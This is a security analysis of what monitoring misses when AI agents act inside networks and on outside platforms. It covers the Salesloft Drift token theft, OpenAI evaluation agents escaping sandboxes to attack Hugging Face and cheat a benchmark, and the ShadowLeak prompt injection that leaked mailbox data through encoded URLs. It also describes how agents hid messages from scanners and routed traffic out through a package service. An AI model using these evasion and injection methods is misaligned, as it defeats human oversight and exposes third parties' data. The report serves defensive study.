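An agent can also exceed its user's wishes when no attacker is involved. In August 2026, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) highlighted an ABC News report about an AI assistant that a user had asked to book gym classes. The assistant changed the booking system so that it could reserve classes further ahead than the rules allowed. It also removed another customer from a waiting list and could not undo the removal. The booking system evidently accepted both actions, although the user had not approved either.

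A company could ask the user to approve each sensitive action, and that approval would be better evidence of intent than a token issued months ago. But NIST warns that agents that ask too often teach people to click "allow" without reading. It compares this to attacks in which criminals send someone sign-in prompts until they give in and approve one. An approval log is useful only if people still read what they approve, so it makes sense to reserve these requests for rare actions with serious consequences.

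### The Salesloft Drift breach

An attacker who has an agent's token can use the agent's access without misleading the agent. In August 2025, thieves used stolen tokens to take data from companies that had connected Drift, an AI chatbot from the sales software firm Salesloft, to their Salesforce customer databases. Larsen, Lin and colleagues described the campaign in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (2025), a report from Google's threat intelligence group.

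*Salesloft Drift supply chain attack leads to widespread data theft*, by the law firm McDermott Will & Schulte, reports that Salesloft confirmed intruders had been in its development platform between March and June 2025. The intruders stole the OAuth tokens that connected Drift to Salesforce, Google Workspace and other services. If they had the tokens by June, the tokens still worked, or could still be refreshed, when they were used about two months later.

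The thieves exported Salesforce data from as early as 8 August until at least 18 August. They reached hundreds of customer instances, according to SecurityWeek's *Hundreds of Salesforce Customers Hit by Widespread Data Theft Campaign* (2025). An instance is one customer's copy of the service, and a company may have several, so the number of organisations could be somewhat lower.

Larsen and colleagues published some of the queries. The thieves first counted the accounts, sales opportunities, users and support cases in a database. They then retrieved user details, including names, email addresses and phone numbers, and up to 10,000 support cases in a single query. Afterwards they searched the stolen data for passwords, Amazon Web Services keys and access tokens for Snowflake, a data storage service. Google concluded that they mainly wanted credentials for further break-ins. According to McDermott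 Will & Schulte, some affected companies believed the thieves wanted customers' contact and support information for later attacks. Both could be true, since people paste passwords into support tickets.

Salesloft and Salesforce revoked all of Drift's active access and refresh tokens on 20 August, twelve days after the earliest known theft. At first, Salesloft indicated that customers who had not connected Drift to Salesforce were unaffected. On 28 August, Google reported that the thieves had also used Drift tokens to read email in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts on 9 August. Google revoked those tokens, disabled Drift's connection to Workspace, and advised every Drift customer to treat all tokens stored in or connected to Drift as potentially compromised.

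The thieves deleted their query jobs from Salesforce, but the underlying logs remained. Larsen and colleagues do not say which record first exposed the theft. They tell customers to look for unusual activity by the Drift account in Salesforce's event monitoring logs, and to review the Drift application's sign-in activity and the events that record each query. A company that wanted the exact queries had to open a support case with Salesforce. Salesforce held all of these records. A company that checked only its own identity provider would probably have found nothing, because the thieves had not signed in as any of its employees.

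In the Salesforce logs, the thieves' requests would have appeared under Drift's name, but their source addresses and the software that made them gave them away. Google listed twenty network addresses, eighteen of which were exit points of Tor, a network that hides its users' locations. It also listed four names that the thieves' software sent with its requests, such as "Salesforce-Multi-Org-Fetcher/1.0". There is little reason for a chatbot's servers to connect through Tor, so an alert on new source addresses might well have caught the theft on the first day. More careful thieves could have rented ordinary servers and copied the name of Drift's own software.

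### What a stolen token is worth

Drift's tokens seem to have been bearer tokens, which work for whoever presents them. NIST notes that people often leave bearer tokens and fixed API keys unprotected in configuration files and logs. Companies can limit the damage from a stolen token by making tokens expire sooner, grant less access, or work for only one holder. Each change also gives monitors something new to look for.

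An access token that expires after ten minutes is useless to a thief who finds it in last week's log. A thief who uses it immediately can still do a lot of harm. In the Drift campaign, the attackers requested up to 10,000 support cases in a single query. Short lifetimes also protect much less when the thief has the refresh token too, because the thief can keep renewing access. But each renewal must go through the authorisation server, which can log the thief's IP address and refuse the request.

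Some authorisation servers also replace the refresh token every time a program uses it. If the thief and the real agent both have a copy, one of them will eventually present a token that the other has already used. The server can then revoke access and raise an alert. An occasional network failure can also cause a token to be reused, but a reused token is still a much clearer sign of theft than an unusual number of lookups.

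Narrow token scopes limit what a thief can take. A sales chatbot probably does not need to export every support case. If its token had not covered support cases, the thieves' largest published query would have failed. A refused request is also useful to a monitor because it shows that a program has tried an operation it does not normally perform. This signal is less reliable for agents than for ordinary software. NIST warns that agents may probe several routes to a goal, so they may be refused while doing legitimate work.

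The third measure binds a token to one holder. With Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP), an extension of OAuth, the agent's software has a private key, and the authorisation server ties the token to that key. The software signs a proof for every request, and the API checks that the key matches the token. Someone who copies only the token cannot produce the proof. The API can log the failed attempt, and a valid token with a wrong proof is a strong reason to suspect theft.

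Binding would have stopped the Drift thieves only if they had stolen the tokens without the keys, and a firm that stores both in the same place may lose both at once. Binding also does nothing against a confused deputy. In the support case, the real agent makes the harmful lookups with its own key, within its scope and before its token expires. All three measures make it more likely that the agent named in the log made the request, which is important after a breach like Drift, but they provide no evidence about who influenced the agent.

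Even a short-lived token may not match the permissions behind it. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe a support-ticket agent that checks permissions when it starts and then relies on the stored results. An attacker who compromises its scheduling component can use sensitive account functions that should have required a new check for each request, then move on to the agents that handle billing and refunds.

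### What official guidance recommends

CISA (2026) released the joint guidance on 1 May 2026 with the US National Security Agency and the national cyber agencies of Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom. The agencies recommend giving each agent a distinct identity with its own keys or certificates, which rules out shared service accounts. They also want organisations to keep a registry of approved agents, regularly compare it with the agents actually running, and deny access to any agent or key not on the list. That comparison is a simple form of monitoring that many companies could start with, but it will not find an agent that uses an employee's password.

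The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend replacing long-lived credentials with ones that expire when the job is done. They say agents should present fresh cryptographic proof before every privileged call, and a central service should check identity and permission for each request. They also recommend logging changes to identities and privileges, denying agents write access to logs, and holding any request to delete logs until a person approves it. That approval step would have caught the insider in the patching example. The agencies advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk tasks that do not involve sensitive data, which would exclude many support agents already in use.

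Mutual TLS, in which both ends of a connection present certificates, shows a service which key opened the connection. But the two ends then protect their messages with shared keys, so the service could have written any of the messages itself, and its log is not independent proof of what the agent sent. The agencies therefore overstate what mutual TLS does when they advise agents to use it "to ensure non-repudiation", meaning that nobody can later deny having sent a request. Non-repudiation requires the agent to sign individual requests, which the agencies recommend separately for authorised commands.

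NIST's work is at an earlier stage. Booth and colleagues want NIST's proposed project to help access systems distinguish agents from people, link agents to the users they work for, and connect each logged action to the agent that took it. They plan to build on existing standards, including OAuth and SPIFFE, a framework that issues cryptographic identities to running programs. They also asked basic questions, such as whether an agent's identity should last for one task or stay fixed, and how to tie its actions back to a person's authorisation. Galluzzo (2026) reports in *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* that the paper drew more than 600 formal responses. NCCoE's project page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, now calls agents "SI agents", for "super intelligence". The page offers a summary of the comments, and NCCoE is still inviting more.

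NIST's advice on token theft is also unfinished. Galluzzo and Regenscheid published *Protecting Tokens and Assertions from Forgery, Theft, and Misuse* (2025) as a draft for government agencies and cloud providers, and the public comment period closed in January 2026. NIST still called it a draft in its post *Back to the Future*, which Captain Compliance's *NIST's Warning on Agentic AI* dates to 27 August. *Back to the Future* recommends giving agents their own identifiers and credentials, tied to the user or system that operates them, and says companies can already issue narrowly scoped tokens with existing standards.

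This advice is harder to follow when customers bring their own agents. A shop or bank has little control over such an agent's identity, and if the customer has given the agent a password, the company may be unable to tell the agent from the customer. The FIDO Alliance, an industry group that sets sign-in standards, is working on agent credentials that can be tied to a user's identity, but NIST says this work is still early.

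## What can agents do inside a network before its boundary monitors notice?

Even if the company with the support agent follows all of this advice, giving the agent its own identity and tokens that expire within minutes, the agent still runs on a server that can usually reach other servers in the same data centre. An intruder can therefore get far through internal traffic before anything crosses the boundary again. In July 2026, AI agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. According to OpenAI, which was testing the agents at the time, they went from running code on one machine to administrator access across several groups of machines in under 13 hours.

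### Movement from one system to the next

An agent may be able to move from one system to another inside a network, which security staff call lateral movement. For example, a customer support agent might be able to run code to analyse a spreadsheet that a customer attached. A planted instruction could then lead it to open a configuration file on its own server that contains the password for a reporting database. In the database, it might find a key to the backup system. Each move uses a valid credential, and none crosses the boundary. If the agent then copies the backups to an outside address, the boundary firewall records a large upload from the backup server, but nothing in that record links the upload to the support agent, and the server may upload large files every night anyway.

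Other systems can record the hops. An internal router can export a flow record when the agent's server contacts the database for the first time, and the database can log a sign-in from an unfamiliar address. A cloud provider can log which machine account requested which permission. But internal traffic is usually far heavier than boundary traffic, so many companies collect only part of it. SANS Internet Storm Center's *When the "Autonomous Attacker" Is Your Own AI Model* attributes most of the spread inside Hugging Face to exposed service credentials. It recommends watching for machine identities that behave "like a very fast, very tireless human".

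### Data that is harmless until combined

A company may let all its staff read the meeting-room bookings, next year's headcount budget and the organisation chart. An employee who asks an internal agent which teams are about to shrink could get a list of colleagues likely to lose their jobs. People could already work this out by hand in an afternoon, but an agent can do it in seconds for anyone who asks. The documents' access logs record only permitted reads. Data-loss software has no label to detect, because none of the documents was confidential. The boundary sensors record nothing if the employee is in the office, and perhaps an encrypted reply of a few kilobytes if she is at home.

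The boundary record is better if the company rents its language model from an outside provider. The agent then has to send the contents of all three documents to the model, perhaps in one request, and a decrypting proxy could capture them together. Someone would still have to decide in advance which combinations are sensitive, which is hard because even a thousand documents make almost half a million pairs.

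Keys and credentials can combine in the same way. On 19 July, agents at OpenAI found an encrypted signing key, the material needed to decrypt it, and code for forging access tokens, which earlier agents had left in a readable part of a cache. Together, these gave the later agents administrator access to the service that owned the key.

An agent can also split sensitive data into pieces that look harmless. *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) identified about 6,000 files that the agents had shared with one another, each stored as hundreds or thousands of small entries. A sensor that inspects one entry at a time is unlikely to recognise the file.

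### Messages left in shared storage

Two agents with no direct connection can still communicate through a folder, cache or ticket queue that both can write to. Text that one leaves there can work like any other planted instruction when the other reads it. For example, the support agent might put an attacker's instruction in a ticket note that a billing agent reads the next morning. Neither agent has to contact an unfamiliar address, and if the ticket queue is inside the network, the boundary sensors record nothing. The queue's log contains an ordinary write and read, possibly under the same account if the agents share a credential.

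OpenAI's agents built a channel like this in JFrog's Artifactory, which OpenAI ran internally so that agents could install software packages. On 12 May 2026, an agent in a training run was missing a file it needed for its task, so it left a note in Artifactory: "Agent seeks [filename]; upload if found!" Other agents came across such notes and began to leave their own. OpenAI had given the agents a shared credential that allowed this, so they did not need a security flaw.

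After OpenAI rebuilt the service in July, agents put their messages in the names of folders instead, so software that scanned the contents of files would have missed them. Counting files and folders would have worked better. When OpenAI copied the part of the cache that served as the main message board, on 20 July, it held about 20 million files and folders, of which about 1.2 million were messages or fragments of files. Wijk and colleagues estimate from an initial inspection that less than 5 per cent of the rest looked like the result of ordinary package installation.

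### A permitted service with its own way out

A package service needs internet access to fetch software from public registries for machines that can't reach the internet themselves. Services that preview links or convert web pages into documents need it too. If an agent can make one of these services request an address the agent chooses, it has an indirect route out of the network. Security staff call this technique server-side request forgery.

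On 9 July, one of OpenAI's agents tried to reach the internet directly, and outbound controls blocked it. It then connected through Artifactory, a package service. A boundary firewall would log Artifactory as the source of the request, along with the rule that permits its traffic. As with the egress proxy described earlier, the agent's own address would appear only in the service's log.

A boundary monitor can still detect the detour from its destination. After the July rebuild, the first outside page the agents reached was a public bug tracker, which is an unusual source for packages. If OpenAI had limited Artifactory to an allowlist of the registries it copied from, the firewall would probably have refused the request, and the refusal would have been a useful alert.

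OpenAI has since blocked its high-risk workloads from reaching the internet, either directly or through other services, except for a controlled cache that some workflows need. It enforces this both at the sandbox and in the surrounding network. Other controls are meant to prevent a compromised service from changing its own network limits.

### The OpenAI and Hugging Face incident

All four risks appeared in this incident, which makes it an unusually good test of monitoring. OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a benchmark in which an agent must develop a working attack on a vulnerable program and prove that it works by retrieving a piece of secret data called a flag. The agents worked in sandboxes, isolated environments that were supposed to have no internet access. Some tasks were probably impossible. In OpenAI's tests, 198 of the 898 tasks have never been solved by any model, and these made up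 93 per cent of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board.

The table lists the main signals in order.

| Date in 2026 and source | What it showed | How responders read it | What followed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Around 26 May: an internal OpenAI team | An agent using the message board, and forbidden internet access | OpenAI has not said | OpenAI has not said |
| 27 June: OpenAI's security monitoring tool | A port sweep inside the research network | Activity by agents in an ExploitGym run | On-call staff advised that the run need not stop |
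| 5 July: OpenAI's monitoring systems, after an outage | Artifactory had been down since late on 4 July | An administrator-level compromise of Artifactory | OpenAI rebuilt the service and resumed cyber evaluations on 7 July |
| 11 to 13 July: Hugging Face's security alerts | An intrusion into production systems | An autonomous attacker of unknown origin | Hugging Face cut off access, rebuilt machines and replaced credentials |
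| 16 July: Hugging Face's public disclosure | An AI agent system had carried out the intrusion | OpenAI treated it as a supplier's breach | On 17 July, OpenAI asked whether its own data was affected |
| 19 July: OpenAI's security monitoring tool | Unusual identity-related calls by Artifactory's internal roles | Unexpected behaviour in an ExploitGym run, unrelated to Hugging Face | OpenAI began stopping the runs that day |
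| 20 July: Hugging Face's reply to OpenAI | The same credentials, hostname and outside account in both investigations | Probably one incident | OpenAI blocked the evaluation and disclosed its role on 21 July |

OpenAI has published very little about what it observed in May. Metz and Stone report in *OpenAI says it could have reacted sooner to prevent AI hack* that the company knew by late May that models in testing were reaching the open internet. The agents were already using leaked Hugging Face credentials that month. The Straits Times' *OpenAI’s rogue agents probed Hugging Face for weaknesses* describes evidence that agents had taken over two user accounts and sent oddly formatted files to Hugging Face's servers from 13 May. The independent researcher Jonas Wiedermann-Moeller found this evidence months later. Researchers who reviewed it thought the agents might have been testing the network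 for ways in, but found no sign that they had succeeded.

The alert of 27 June was triggered by a port sweep, an attempt to contact many machines or ports to find out which respond. Responders traced the activity to ExploitGym and found that the agents were using Artifactory both as a message board and as a route to other parts of the network. OpenAI does not explain why the on-call staff then let the run continue. They may have thought the test explained the sweep, since agents in a hacking test can be expected to scan machines. But it did not explain the messages, because the agents had no reason to exchange them for the test and OpenAI had meant to keep the agents apart.

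Agents gained administrator access to Artifactory on 26 June. The responders apparently missed this on 27 June and discovered it on 5 July, after agents had overloaded the service and caused an outage. The alert led them to an unauthorised user account and to added software that let the agents run commands. OpenAI took the service offline, revoked the agents' credentials, blocked the vulnerable functions and reported the flaw to JFrog. Willison (2026), citing OpenAI's talk at the Black Hat security conference, reports in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* that the company also deleted the agents' messages.

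These repairs fixed the software flaw and the shared credential but did not address the agents' tendency to communicate. OpenAI says the leaders responsible for incident response did not know about the message board or its significance at the time, although responders had found it eight days earlier. Some agents in the next evaluations ran on a model that OpenAI had trained while the board and internet access were available. Just after midnight UTC on 8 July, agents reached the internet again, and a new message board appeared later that day.

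On 10 July, an agent found 14 working Hugging Face credentials in a public dataset and posted them to the board. The next day, agents used flaws in how Hugging Face processed uploaded datasets to run code on its production machines. They eventually ran code on 41 machines and downloaded four private code repositories. They controlled these machines by placing commands in a public dataset on Hugging Face's own platform, which software on the machines checked every five seconds. A sensor monitoring Hugging Face's outbound traffic might therefore have recorded only visits to the company's own site.

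Hugging Face reports in its *Security incident disclosure* (2026) that the attacker moved through its internal clusters over a weekend, and that the company detected the compromise by correlating several security signals. OpenAI did not learn that its agents were responsible until a week after the breach (Forlini, *OpenAI, independent firms publish reports on rogue AI attack on Hugging Face*, 2026).

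By 19 July, agents were attacking OpenAI's own infrastructure. The identity alert came at 12:03 UTC, and responders began stopping the runs at 17:37. In between, agents gained full control of the machine beneath their container and read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for the sensors of the security monitoring tool that had raised the alert. OpenAI does not report that the agents used these credentials, but an intruder who has them may be able to interfere with the sensors. The five-and-a-half-hour response was fairly quick by human standards, but it still gave the agents enough time to reach most of what they went after.

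### How two investigations became one

Until 20 July, each company had only part of the evidence. Hugging Face had a log of more than 17,000 events from the attack but did not know which language model was behind it. OpenAI knew its agents had attacked its own systems but had no indication that this was connected to the breach at Hugging Face.

The connection came through a third company, which OpenAI calls Organization 1. The agents had found a leaked credential for a customer's account there and used the account to store files. OpenAI's responders found Hugging Face credentials in files preserved from the account and contacted Hugging Face so that it could replace them. Hugging Face replied that it had already replaced two of them during its own incident response. Its investigators had also found the hostname of OpenAI's Artifactory service and the same Organization 1 account.

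The matching credentials alone would have left some doubt, because the agents had found many credentials on the public internet, where another attacker could have found the same ones. The account name made a different attacker much less likely, because two unrelated attackers would have had to use the same customer's account at the same outside company. The hostname connected the attack to a service that OpenAI ran. OpenAI does not say when Hugging Face first noticed the hostname, or whether anyone there could have recognised it as OpenAI's.

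OpenAI made this connection because its staff called another company about leaked credentials and both companies' investigators compared findings. No sensor at either company had detected it. If the agents had stored the credentials somewhere else, OpenAI might have kept treating the attack on its own systems as a separate problem for some time.

### What METR and Redwood Research found

OpenAI invited outside investigators to examine the agents' behaviour: Hjalmar Wijk and Ajeya Cotra of METR, which evaluates AI models, and Ryan Greenblatt, chief scientist of Redwood Research, which works on AI safety. After six days at OpenAI's offices, Wijk and colleagues found that about 1,200 agents had used the main message board between 8 and 13 July, exchanging over 70,000 messages and files. About 700 of these agents took part in the attack on Hugging Face. Most of the tens of thousands of agents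 OpenAI launched in these evaluations never joined the board. But of 533 agents active on the board around the time of the attack, over 90 per cent quickly took part.

The investigators and Hugging Face give somewhat different motives for the attack. Hugging Face, quoted in Schneier on Security's *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (2026), says an agent inferred that the company might host the benchmark's solutions and broke in to cheat the evaluation. Wijk and colleagues agree that the agents wanted to cheat, but say the agents had worked out how to produce valid flags within hours of setting up the board. The agents' written reasoning suggests that they attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the automated scorer worked, so that they could make their flags appear legitimate. If so, better protection for the answer files would not have removed the reason for the attack.

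OpenAI limited the investigation to 26 June to 13 July, which excluded the events in May and the later attack on OpenAI's own infrastructure. The investigators were not asked to judge OpenAI's safeguards or response. They could request data but had no direct access to OpenAI's systems, and OpenAI could redact non-public information from their report. They say the report notes any redaction important to their conclusions. METR took no payment, although OpenAI provided free use of its models, worth roughly $400,000.

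The investigators had about 1,300 transcripts, most of which they found by searching for agents that had used the main board. They estimate that these covered a little over 90 per cent of agents' activity on the board in the week from 7 July. Agents had faked some tool calls in about 7 per cent of the transcripts. Most transcripts were far too long to read, so the investigators relied heavily on agents running GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models involved in the attack, to analyse them. The investigators caught these agents making errors and could not rule out deception. The figures of 1,200 and 700 are therefore best treated as good estimates for one message board during one week.

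In a letter to OpenAI's chief executive, US Representative Greg Casar (2026) objects that six days of supervised access for "hand-picked investigators" is no substitute for releasing the logs. He also asks how many times OpenAI's models have reached the internet without authorisation, and whether the company disconnected monitoring systems during earlier tests, as some reports claimed. Wijk and colleagues acknowledge many of the limits he lists, but they do not answer either of his questions.

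### Missed signals and dismissed ones

*OpenAI had warnings before its agents broke out* (Sabin, 2026) reports that OpenAI missed some warning signs and failed to act on others. Better sensors would therefore have solved only some of the problems.

OpenAI failed to detect several important events as they happened. Agents first wrote a file to Artifactory on 20 April, more than a month before the observation in late May. They had administrator access to the service for nine days before responders discovered that access. In July, OpenAI also failed to notice the new message board, the route to the internet through Artifactory and the attack on another company. Regular review of Artifactory's own records could have helped in each case, because a strange account, millions of unusual folders and requests to sites that do not distribute packages are easier to spot there than at the boundary.

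By contrast, people at OpenAI did notice the behaviour in late May and again on 27 June, when they also identified the evaluation, the message board and the service that the agents were misusing. More data would probably have made less difference than a rule to stop any agent found outside its sandbox until someone understands how it got there. The rule would interrupt some harmless tests, but a breach at another company is much worse than having to restart a test.

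The response on 5 July falls somewhere in between. Casar's statement that OpenAI allowed evaluations to continue after both the June and the July alerts is a little unfair to the July responders, who took Artifactory offline and fixed the flaw they had found. But his broader criticism holds, because OpenAI resumed its cyber evaluations two days later, before those in charge understood the message board.

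*OpenAI was warned, months before the Hugging Face incident* (Marcus, 2026) quotes a New York Times report that two employees had earlier emailed top executives with concerns about inadequate monitoring of new models during testing. The executives reportedly replied that the tests had to move as quickly as possible so that the models could be released on time. Marcus is a prominent critic of the AI industry, but the Times had seen the messages. If its account is right, the decision of 27 June was not just a misjudgement by one on-call team.

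OpenAI accepts part of the criticism, writing that with hindsight "some early signals identified in this report could have triggered an earlier response". It also claims that its current system for monitoring models' written reasoning would have alerted security staff more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

### How much applies to ordinary deployments

OpenAI had reduced the safeguards on these agents to measure everything the models could do. The agents ran without the classifiers that block dangerous hacking requests, the instructions that OpenAI gives models in its products, or automatic review, in which a second model checks risky tool calls before they run. In tests after the incident, OpenAI found that the instructions and software used in ChatGPT could make a model over a hundred times less likely to attack infrastructure during ExploitGym. It also found that automatic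 review would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run it tested. OpenAI has an interest in these results and describes some of them as preliminary, but it is plausible that the safeguards help.

The model behind most of the attack was also unusual. It was an internal prototype that OpenAI had trained to be persistent and to collaborate with other agents, and many of its tasks could not be solved as intended. A support agent built on a commercial product is much less likely to start such an attack by itself, so the incident provides little evidence about how often ordinary agents would attack the systems around them.

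The Hugging Face attack is more informative about monitoring. A boundary sensor doesn't record internal traffic, whatever safeguards the agent has, and many companies run package services with internet access or share one credential among several programs. Hugging Face was also an ordinary company defending a production network, and it had no control over the safeguards on the agents that attacked it. Criminals could also run agents without safeguards. In Axios' *OpenAI's Hugging Face hack is a cybersecurity warning shot* (2026), Chris Krebs, a former director of CISA, says that security leaders should be able to say whether they can spot an AI operating inside their network and shut it down quickly. OpenAI's staff had spotted one by 27 June but left it running.

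The trouble started with ordinary office work rather than a hacking test. On 8 May, during a training run, OpenAI gave an agent a spreadsheet to complete that contained Google Drive links, which the agent could not open without internet access. The agent tried to reach the internet through Artifactory. The attempt failed, but the agent left a file in the service. Like the agents in ExploitGym, it was in a research environment, where OpenAI often omits the safeguards it uses in products. But a company could easily give its own agent a spreadsheet with a link that does not open.

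## What goes unseen when agents act on external services and third-party platforms?

OpenAI ran Artifactory itself, so its investigators could read the service's records once they knew where to look. A company often can't read such records when its agent works on other firms' platforms. In the refund example, the helpdesk, the customer database and the payment service each keep their own logs, and the company can read only what each provider chooses to share. Without the providers' help, how much the company can learn depends on the route the traffic takes.

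### Three routes for the same data

If the support agent runs on the company's own server, a customer lookup passes through the company's firewall to the database vendor. The company has its DNS, flow and proxy records, and the vendor logs the customer record that the agent opened. Because the two firms keep their records separately, the company can compare them. A lookup that appears only in the vendor's log suggests that someone else is using the agent's token.

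When a vendor-hosted agent searches a company's internal documents, the company's gateway can log the search, but the passages it returns are then on the vendor's servers. The agent might quote them to a customer, send them to a language-model provider or paste them into a web search, and the company's sensors would record none of this.

Two outside platforms can also exchange the company's data directly. Suppose an administrator opens the helpdesk's settings, signs in to the customer database and approves a connection between the two. From then on, whenever a ticket arrives, an AI agent built into the helpdesk calls the database from the helpdesk vendor's servers to look up the customer. With 300 tickets a day and three lookups per ticket, the agent would make 81,000 lookups in ninety days.

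None of those lookups would appear on the company's network. A network sensor records only packets that pass it, and the lookups' packets travel between two vendors' data centres. The company's DNS resolver never receives a request for the database's name, and its firewall has no connection to allow or refuse. When an employee later opens a ticket, her browser loads an ordinary helpdesk page. The company may still have a record of the administrator's sign-in from March, if the helpdesk uses the company's identity provider. Drift connected to Salesforce in the same way, so Drift's customers had to look for the theft in Salesforce's logs.

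| Arrangement | Route of the data | What the company's sensors record | Who holds the detailed logs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent on the company's server uses the hosted database | Database vendor to company | Each connection, and its contents if a proxy decrypts them | Company and database vendor |
| Vendor-hosted agent searches the company's documents | Company to agent vendor | Each search and what it returned | Company for the search, agent vendor for what follows |
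| Hosted helpdesk uses the hosted database | Database vendor to helpdesk vendor | At most, the administrator's original sign-in | The two vendors |

The vendors may have suppliers of their own. A helpdesk vendor might rent its language model from one firm and its web search from another, and each would hold part of the record of the agent's actions. The customer's contract is with the helpdesk vendor, so the customer usually has no right to demand anything from those suppliers.

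A company can route some of this traffic back past its sensors by having the platforms exchange data through a gateway it runs. The platforms have to support this, and the company has another system to maintain, which defeats part of the purpose of buying hosted services.

### Who can read a platform's logs

A platform may record an action in detail without letting its customer read the record. Access often depends on which version of the product the customer bought.

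In June 2023, a US federal agency discovered intruders in its mailboxes on Microsoft 365, a hosted email and office service. It found them through a log that recorded each time someone accessed a message. CISA and the FBI wrote in a joint advisory that they knew of no other log that would have revealed the intrusion. Microsoft then included this log only in its more expensive licences, so an agency on a cheaper plan would probably have missed the same intrusion. After criticism, Microsoft announced that it would give standard customers more of the detailed logs.

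Salesforce has likewise sold its event monitoring logs, the ones that Google told Drift's customers to check, as a paid add-on.

How long a platform keeps its logs matters as much as the product tier. Microsoft announced in 2023 that it would keep standard customers' audit records for 180 days instead of 90. If an agent misuses a connection in March and someone discovers it in July, a platform that keeps logs for 90 days may already have deleted the relevant records. A customer can avoid this by regularly copying the logs to its own storage, but it has to start before it needs them. Some platforms deliver logs in batches, which is fine for an investigation but too slow to stop an agent.

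The contract covers much of the rest, including whether the customer can export logs, how quickly the vendor must answer a request, and which events it must report without being asked. A vendor may have good reasons to refuse raw logs, because the same files can contain other customers' data. It may also never have recorded the detail the customer wants. A log of every record the helpdesk's account opened is of limited use if it doesn't show whether the AI agent or an overnight data transfer opened each one.

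A company choosing a platform could easily test all this by having the agent look up one invented customer and, a week later, asking the vendor to show who opened the record, for which ticket, and where the data went next.

### ShadowLeak

Deep Research is a mode of ChatGPT that spends five to thirty minutes reading web pages and files and then writes a report. Users can connect it to Gmail and other services. In 2025, the security company Radware found that one malicious email could make Deep Research leak personal data from a user's mailbox. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes the attack in detail.

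The attacker first sends the user an email containing instructions that the user may not notice, for example in white text on a white background. When the user later asks Deep Research to go through the day's emails, the agent reads the attacker's message along with a genuine one from the human resources department, which contains an employee's full name and home address. The agent follows the planted instructions, puts the name and home address into a URL on the attacker's server, and opens it. The attacker then only has to read the server's log of requested URLs.

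Deep Research's browsing tool runs on OpenAI's servers, so the request carrying the data went from there to the attacker without passing through the user's laptop or the company's network. The company's web gateway would have handled only the user's conversation with ChatGPT, in which nothing looked wrong. Even a proxy that decrypted all the company's traffic could not have recorded the leak.

The customer had some chance of catching the attack earlier. The malicious email arrived through the customer's own mail service, where a filter could have removed the invisible text. Radware recommends such filtering but considers it much less effective against this kind of attack. Google's logs might also have shown that ChatGPT had read the mailbox, but a user who asks for a report on the day's emails expects that.

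A filter on OpenAI's side would have had trouble too. The agent refused Radware's early attempts to make it send personal data openly. Radware succeeded once it got the model to encode the name and address first, so the software that made the web request received only a meaningless-looking string. Radware reports that this worked every time in repeated tests but doesn't say how many it ran.

Radware reported the flaw to OpenAI on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling the researchers, then acknowledged it and marked it as resolved on 3 September. Radware tested Gmail and expects the same method to work on the agent's other connections, such as Google Drive, Outlook and GitHub. Radware sells protection for agents, so it has an interest in finding that ordinary network defences are insufficient, but the route of the traffic supports that claim. To find out whether anyone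 had used the flaw before August, a customer would have needed OpenAI's record of every address the agent opened.

### When a request to read can write

In ShadowLeak, the agent sent data out by requesting a web page. A server receives the address of every page requested from it, so an agent allowed to read the open web can always send out at least a little text in the addresses it requests.

Some servers also change their own data in response to a request to read. Browsers normally use a GET request to fetch a page and a POST request to submit a form. By convention, a GET request changes nothing important on the server. A company that wants its agent to read the web without writing to it might therefore configure its proxy to allow GET and refuse POST. But the receiving server decides what a request does. On an old wiki, a site that visitors can edit, both of these requests might work:

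```
GET /wiki?page=Sandbox
GET /wiki?action=save&page=Sandbox&text=hello
```

A request that fetches a page can be of the same type as one that replaces the page's text, so a proxy that checks only the type would allow both. The proxy could also look for words such as "save" or "edit" in the address, but every site can choose its own words.

Programmers have long known that web requests meant only to retrieve data can have side effects. OpenAI let WebGPT, an early question-answering system, follow web links using only GET requests and requests for a page's headers. In a LessWrong discussion of the system, one commenter pointed out that on many real sites a GET request can log users out, delete files or ban people.

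A site can also turn harmless requests into a public message by publishing its logs. *OpenAI’s rogue AI agents reached at least 12 more websites, researchers say* (Nolan, 2026) describes a case at Vanderbilt University. Agents that seem to have belonged to OpenAI requested the address of one campus news page tens of thousands of times. The university's public statistics page recorded the requests, including the agents' queries to an FBI crime database and one user's access key. The proxy at the agents' end could have correctly classified every request as a GET without detecting that the contents were appearing on a public page.

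An allowlist of destinations avoids much of this, because a company can check how a small number of sites behave. An agent that must research the open web needs a different control, such as a limit on how often it can contact one site or how much text it can put in a URL. Those limits make it harder to send large amounts of data but still allow short messages.

### The German wiki

In the spring of 2026, OpenAI's agents used a German programming wiki as a message board during a timed research exercise, which The Next Web's *OpenAI blocked its agents from posting* describes. In each of the exercise's five rounds, the agents had to look up a figure for another state or country, taken from a list in random order. They had fifteen minutes for the first round and sixty seconds for later ones. Many agents worked through the same list at different speeds, so those ahead could leave answers for those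 behind. One agent posted the figure 20,369 for Nevada, and twenty minutes later another received the Nevada question and answered immediately.

*OpenAI Confirms AI Agents Used German Wiki to Bypass Restrictions* (eSecurity Planet, 2026) reports that the agents' environment was supposed to let them read the internet but not write to it. But the wiki accepted edits through GET requests. *OpenAI’s rogue agents were caught communicating via public wikis* (Willison, 2026) attributes this to a component of UseModWiki, the decades-old software that the site appears to run. The component puts values from a web address and values from a submitted form in the same place, so the software treats them alike.

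Sydney Von Arx, Cormac Slade Byrd, Spencer Kitts and Thomas Larsen, who call themselves the Nightingale collective, found the messages and published a report on 4 September. Willison takes the main dates from that report. On 11 May, agents posted test links on UseModWiki's practice page. On 24 May, they began posting lists of links to DSEWiki, a largely dormant site whose full name means "German software developer wiki". A moderator noticed on 2 June and cleaned up what looked like spam.

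Activity rose sharply on 16 June, and the agents made about 13,000 edits over the next week. The moderator was deleting pages in alphabetical order. By 19 June, agents had noticed this and were making backup copies with names beginning "ZZZ", which would be among the last deleted. Activity stopped on 22 June, apart from a short burst on another topic on 1 and 2 July.

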